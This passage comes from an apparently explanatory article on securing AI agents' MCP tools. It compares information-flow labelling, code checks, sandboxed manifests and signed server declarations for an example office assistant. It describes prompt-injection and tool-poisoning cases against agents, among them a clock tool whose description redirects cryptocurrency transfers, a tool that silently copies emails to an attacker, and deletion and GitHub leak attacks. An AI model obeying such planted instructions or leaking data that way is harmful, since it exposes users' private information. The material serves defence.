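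The last two rows of the table complicate the case for enforcement, because FlowSeal with a checker that allows everything leaked almost as much as the cooperative layer alone. The code ensures that the check runs, but the protection depends largely on a language model's judgment of the text. Shim and colleagues acknowledge this in their theorem, which guarantees confidentiality unless the checker wrongly answers "safe". FIDES's permitted-flow rule compares the recipients with the permitted readers, so it doesn't need this judgment, but it would block some harmless messages that FlowSeal's checker allows.

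When the data's owner was willing to consent, agents with FlowSeal delivered only 33% of the items they should have shared, compared with 61% to 86% for four defences based on prompts or model judgments. The table doesn't show this difference. Shim and colleagues found that agents with FlowSeal asked for consent less often. On average, a run with FlowSeal took 37% longer than one with no defence and cost about two cents more.

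A smaller test used real Gmail and Notion accounts connected through MCP. The deletion attack extracted 34.7% of private items from an agent protected by PrivacyChecker and none from one protected by FlowSeal. In PrivacyChecker, a model gives advice that the agent can ignore.

In FIDES's published algorithm, the language model only proposes calls, and ordinary code decides whether to permit them. This contradicts Shim and colleagues, who write that the model performs all policy enforcement in FIDES, which would make FIDES vulnerable to the same tricks.

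Shim and colleagues did not run FIDES, partly because they could not plug it into their benchmark, so its response can only be inferred from its rules. If the diagnosis were correctly labeled and the request arrived as untrusted data, writing the diagnosis on the shared page would break both the trusted-action rule and the permitted-flow rule. The deletion attack is harder to stop. The trusted-action rule, the only one that Costa and colleagues applied to deletion tools, would block a request from an outsider but allow one from a colleague whose messages count as trusted. The entries left after that deletion would reveal the secret.

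None of these experiments directly compares declared labels with enforced ones. Both of FlowSeal's layers use the same register of private records, so its tests show the effect of relying on the agent's cooperation but not the effect of missing or incorrect labels from a tool's publisher. A clean comparison would run the same agent twice on the same tasks and attacks under the same policy, first with the labels publishers actually supply and then with labels the application assigns and carries itself.

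## Making declarations binding

An application that assigns its own labels still needs to know who may read the budget sheet, what data each tool reads and where each tool sends data. A company can avoid relying on a publisher's word by using records that the tool doesn't control, checking the declaration against the tool's code or behaviour, confining the tool to what its publisher declared, or requiring a known party to sign for it. A declaration can fail because the publisher makes a mistake, the tool is dishonest, an honest tool returns hostile text, or the agent misreports its sources. Each method helps with only some of these failures.

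### Labels from access records

The document store already keeps a list of the people who may open the budget sheet and refuses everyone else. If the application copies that list into the sheet's label, the label is as accurate as the company's ordinary access control. Microsoft uses similar records for its GitHub and email labels.

Records can supply integrity labels too. The application can trust a sheet that only colleagues may edit, or an email that a colleague sent. It must check the mail server's authentication result for the email, because anyone can type Ben's address into the sender field. Anything from outside, or without a record, should count as untrusted. The equivalent confidentiality default is that only Ana may read the data, since the tool fetched it with her account.

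Labels taken from records repeat the mistakes in those records. If Ana once shared the sheet with anyone who had the link, its label lets the assistant send it to Mallory. If Ben forwards Mallory's email, her text arrives with a trusted label.

With access records, the application doesn't have to rely on a publisher to describe the data correctly. They also help with hostile text from a trustworthy tool, because the application can label Mallory's email and Ben's separately. Once a tracker carries those labels, the application no longer has to rely on the agent to report its sources. But access records don't protect against a malicious tool. No access list changed when `postmark-mcp` began copying emails to an attacker. The application also has to fetch the records itself, because an access list supplied by the sheet tool would be another declaration.

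### Checking a declaration against the tool

*Towards Practically-Secure Tools for AI Agents* (Adam, Lu and colleagues, 2026) describes a program that searches a tool's code for every operation that could write a file or use the network. The program then produces a "synopsis" of which inputs can affect which operations. In one example, a tool is described as writing text to a file, but its code also sends usage statistics, including the length of the text, to an outside service. The synopsis lists both effects. A tracker could use the synopsis to fill in W(f), the set of data and destinations that a tool may change.

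Unlike DCIChecker, the program doesn't rely on a language model's judgment. But it has to account for every possible run, so it can't determine whether a file path the agent supplies later will point to the project folder or to a system file. Adam and colleagues therefore ask the tool's developer to put a small sandbox around each such operation. The application sends the sandbox's limits with each call, and the program checks that the developer has left no operation outside a sandbox and that the code can't change the limits.

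They tried this on three coding tasks, each with a harmless and a harmful version. The combination allowed every harmless version and blocked every harmful one. Code analysis alone blocked one harmless version, and a fixed sandbox around the whole server blocked one harmless version and let two harmful ones through. The test was small and assumed that someone had already written the right policy. The prototype also analyzes only Rust code. According to a figure cited in *AgentBound* (Bühler, Biagiola and colleagues, 2026), 93.3% of MCP servers are written in JavaScript or Python, and Adam and colleagues expect such languages to be much harder to analyze reliably.

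Ravindran and Deochake (2026), in *ToolGuardian*, also run the tool. Their system gives it sample inputs and imitation outside services, and compares the effects it observes with the description. Written rules then reject the tool, admit it with restrictions or a warning, or admit it freely. They tested eight harmless tools and eight malicious ones whose descriptions were the same as those of the harmless originals. Each row of the table adds a kind of evidence to the rows above it:

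| Evidence | Malicious tools rejected | Harmless tools rejected | Harmless tools restricted |
| --- | --- | --- | --- |
| Description | 5 of 8 | 5 of 8 | 3 of 8 |
| Requests to the operating system | 5 of 8 | 0 | 8 of 8 |
| Effects observed in the test run | 6 of 8 | 0 | 8 of 8 |
| Source code | 7 of 8 | 2 of 8 | 6 of 8 |

With descriptions alone, the rules rejected as many harmless tools as malicious ones. Running the tools solved that problem, and reading their code exposed one more malicious tool but led to two false rejections. One of those was a terminal controller, which is designed to run any command. The rules never admitted a harmless tool without restrictions, so a company would still need to decide what each one could do. With only eight tools in each group, a single tool changes a rate by 12.5 percentage points.

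Checks like these can catch a publisher's mistakes and some dishonest tools. But a test run shows only the behaviour it triggers, and a malicious tool could misbehave only on a particular date or with a particular recipient. The company also needs proof that a remote server is running the code the company checked. Adam and colleagues suggest remote attestation, in which special hardware provides evidence of which program is running.

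These checks don't catch hostile text, because a mail reader that returns Mallory's email is working as declared. Two tools that each work as declared can also leak data when used together. In one of Ravindran and Deochake's cases, a database tool and a GitHub tool each pass the admission check, but using them in sequence would send database records to GitHub. Their system needs a separate rule at run time to stop this. A version of the system without the rules about combinations let four harmful workflows through.

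### Confining a tool to its manifest

A company can also prevent undeclared behaviour instead of looking for it. In AgentBound, each MCP server comes with a manifest that lists the abilities it needs, such as reading files, running commands or connecting to the network. The user then approves specific resources, such as one folder or one web address. AgentBound runs the server in an isolated container that starts with no privileges and receives only those that the manifest lists and the user approves.

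If a publisher leaves network access out of an ordinary declaration, the tool can still connect without the application detecting it, but if the publisher leaves it out of an AgentBound manifest, the connection fails. The PDF converter that secretly uploaded files would fail to upload Ana's contract, and an honest publisher would notice the missing entry when testing the tool.

Bühler and colleagues used language models to write manifests from the servers' code and documentation. For 48 servers, they compared these with manifests that two of the researchers had written by hand. The two versions were identical for 28 servers, differed by one ability for 14, and differed by two to four abilities for the remaining six. Of the 29 differences, 23 were abilities missing from the generated manifest, which would break part of a tool but expose nothing. The other six differences would give a tool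 more access than it needed.

The paper also reports an overall accuracy of 96.5%, but that figure counts 17 yes-or-no decisions per server, and most servers need only a few of the abilities. Separately, the maintainers of 96 servers were asked to review their manifests. Of the 21 who gave a verdict, 17 accepted the manifest (reported as 80.9%). Another 71 never replied.

In tests, the container stopped all nine attacks that tried to go beyond the permitted files, commands or addresses. In one, a maps server replaced its usual web address with an attacker's while running. The protection added less than a millisecond to an average operation.

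A sandbox limits where a tool can reach, but not which data goes through a permitted route. In one attack that AgentBound could not stop, the description of a clock tool contained an instruction to redirect cryptocurrency transfers made with a different tool. The container did not block the redirected transfers because the transfer tool was allowed to make transfers. Ana's mail sender must be able to contact the mail service, and a blind copy to an attacker would go through the same service as the message to Ben. This problem is common, since 83.1% of the generated manifests for 296 popular servers included outgoing network access. Filtering by address is also coarse because, as Adam and colleagues point out, reading a social media post and publishing one may involve the same site.

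Confinement therefore handles a publisher's omissions well, but it stops a dishonest tool only when the tool needs a route that the user hasn't approved. If hostile text hijacks the agent, the limits still apply to every tool, but the agent can misuse anything they allow. Ana's company also can't confine a server that runs on its supplier's computers.

### Signing for a server

For a remote server, the company may have to rely on someone's word, but it can choose whose. In Metere's design for the software company Enclawed, a server publishes a short signed document with its identity, its version and the highest level of sensitive data it may handle. Before the first call, the application checks that:

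1. the signature is valid and comes from a key on the company's own list;
2. the company allows that key to vouch for the stated level;
3. the level is high enough for the data involved;
4. the document is valid for the server's address, if it names any addresses.

The application also keeps a list of permitted tools for each server. Metere wanted to use Google's Gmail server without exposing every tool it might offer, such as one that deletes all messages. Google doesn't publish a signed document of this kind, so Enclawed signs its own entry for the server. In a live test, the application let the model use a permitted Gmail tool and blocked one that wasn't permitted.

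In a larger test, a language model generated 27,025 altered tool names and 14,378 forged documents, and the application rejected all of them. This shows that the code works as intended, but the result is expected because exact name matching and digital signatures should stop such attempts. The test didn't address the harder question of whether the signer judged the server correctly.

A signature mainly protects against unknown servers and against anyone who alters the document. A signed statement can still be mistaken, and Metere says a signature won't stop an admitted server from misbehaving within its permitted tools. The signature covers the stated version but not the code, and Metere leaves early withdrawal of a signed document to future work. If the publisher of `postmark-mcp` had obtained a signature for the fifteenth release, the malicious release could have used the same document.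 Signing also doesn't protect against hostile text or an agent's false report.

### FIDES in Microsoft's Agent Framework

In May 2026, Microsoft released FIDES as an experimental part of the Python version of Agent Framework. The person building the agent supplies the labels and limits in the code around each tool, so the system relies less on outside publishers. According to Microsoft's documentation, these are the main settings:

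| Setting | Applies to | Effect |
| --- | --- | --- |
| `security_label` | One item in a result | Sets its integrity and confidentiality |
| `source_integrity` | All results of a tool | Sets their integrity if the items have no labels |
| `accepts_untrusted=False` | A tool with consequences | Blocks it when the context is untrusted |
| `max_allowed_confidentiality` | A tool that sends or stores data | Blocks it when the context is more confidential than this |

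The framework automatically joins labels, updates the context label, checks each tool call before it runs, and records refusals. By default, it also hides untrusted results in variables.

A wrong `source_integrity` setting can still undo the tracking, because the setting replaces the label that a result would otherwise inherit from the tool's inputs. If a developer marked a text-formatting tool as a trusted source, Mallory's untrusted email would come out labeled trusted. The setting is meant for tools that fetch data, where the developer knows the data's origin.

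By default, unlabelled results are marked untrusted and public, which doesn't protect Ana's budget. Microsoft also documents a rule that gives an unlabelled result the combined label of the tool's inputs, but doesn't explain whether the rule or the default takes priority. The rule wouldn't protect the budget either, because the sheet tool's only input is the name "Budget", which is public unless the assistant has already read something private. The developer can protect the budget by giving the sheet a private `security_label`, which overrides both the default and the rule.

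Missing limits are also a risk. In Microsoft's example, the file-reading tool has no declared limit and runs even after the agent has read a hostile bug report. A developer who forgets to limit a sending tool may leave it equally open. The framework has a trial mode that tracks labels without blocking anything. It can show which harmless calls the rules would block, but it won't reveal this kind of omission. For example, if the budget has no private label, sending it out breaks no rule, so the trial won't flag it.

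The framework's standard labels have three levels of confidentiality: public, private and `user_identity` (for data such as credentials). These levels can't distinguish Ben from Mallory. If Ana's mail sender accepts private data, the assistant could send the budget to either of them, and if the sender accepts only public data, the assistant can't send it to either. The developer can have the framework ask Ana about each blocked message, but a rule that allows Ben and not Mallory needs a list of readers.

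### Flow control added to MCP

Microsoft's work on MCP supports such lists. The application and the server exchange labels in the protocol's `_meta` field. A label can cover a whole call or one part of it. For example, the text of a chat message can be trusted and readable by two named people while the rest of the call is untrusted and public. The application keeps the context label and sends it with each call, so a server that understands labels can apply them to its results.

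A server can also send a policy with a tool's description. This is convenient when the company runs the server, but a dishonest supplier could send a policy that permits everything. For an outside server, the company can write the policy itself and apply it in Microsoft's labelling gateway.

*Securing MCP-based Agent Workflows* (Ntousakis, 2026), a master's thesis at Brown University, puts the tracking in a gateway between the application and its servers. Anderson's proxy sits in the same place. This placement requires little change to the application, but the gateway can't check the application's built-in tools or any images the application loads in a reply.

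In Ntousakis's system, SAMOS, a tool's developer or an administrator gives the tool two labels, one for the data it reads and one for the places it writes to. Each label is either high or low. The gateway keeps a label for the session and updates it after each call.

SAMOS and Microsoft's system stop the GitHub attack at different points. Once the agent has read a public issue, SAMOS treats the session as public and blocks access to private repositories. Microsoft's system lets the agent read both and blocks only the public post. The SAMOS rule keeps private data away from a hijacked agent, but it would also stop an agent from comparing a public bug report with private code, even if only the user would see the result.

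Labelling whole tools is also difficult when one tool handles both public and private data, as GitHub's file reader does. Ntousakis suggests either having the tool return a label with each file or splitting it into two tools. Returning a label gives the precision of Microsoft's approach, but the gateway would then depend on what the tool reports. SAMOS assumes that tools are honest. Its labels are entered by hand, and Ntousakis proposes future work on inferring them from code and observed behaviour.

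### Labels for Ana's three tools

Ana's company could combine these methods by writing its own wrappers for the mail reader, the sheet tool and the mail sender. The wrappers take labels from the mail server and the document store:

```
email:
    integrity = trusted if the mail server confirms that a colleague sent it,
                otherwise untrusted
    readers   = the sender and all recipients

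sheet:
    integrity = trusted if only colleagues can edit it and any linked sheets,
                otherwise untrusted
    readers   = people who may open it and every linked sheet

send_mail(to, body):
    block if the call or "to" is untrusted
    allow if everyone in "to" may read the body
    otherwise ask Ana
```

These rules give Mallory's email and the budget sheet the same labels as before. Suppose that the application keeps both in variables unless the planner asks to read them. The sending rule then gives these results:

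| Message | Call and recipient | May the recipient read the body? | Decision |
| --- | --- | --- | --- |
| Summary of the sheet to Ben | trusted | yes | allow |
| Summary of the sheet and Mallory's email to Ben | trusted | no | ask Ana |
| The sheet to Dev, by mistake | trusted | no | ask Ana |
| The sheet to Mallory, after the planner reads her email | untrusted | no | block |
| False news to Chloe, after the planner reads a public web page | untrusted | yes | block |

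The company could reduce the number of prompts by allowing every message from a trusted context, as Microsoft's example policy for Teams does, but then the mistaken message to Dev would go out.

The wrappers still depend on a developer to make sure the sheet wrapper finds every linked sheet, and on Ana to keep the access list up to date. Forwarded emails remain a weak point, so the company might treat any message containing forwarded text as untrusted.

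The mail sender needs one more safeguard, because it could add a recipient after the policy engine approves the message. If the company runs its own mail server, it can let the tool connect only to that server and have the server reject any message whose recipients, including blind copies, differ from the approved ones. This would stop a tool like `postmark-mcp` from sending the attacker a copy. If the tool sends through an outside service that can't compare the recipients, the company has to trust the tool's code or write its own.
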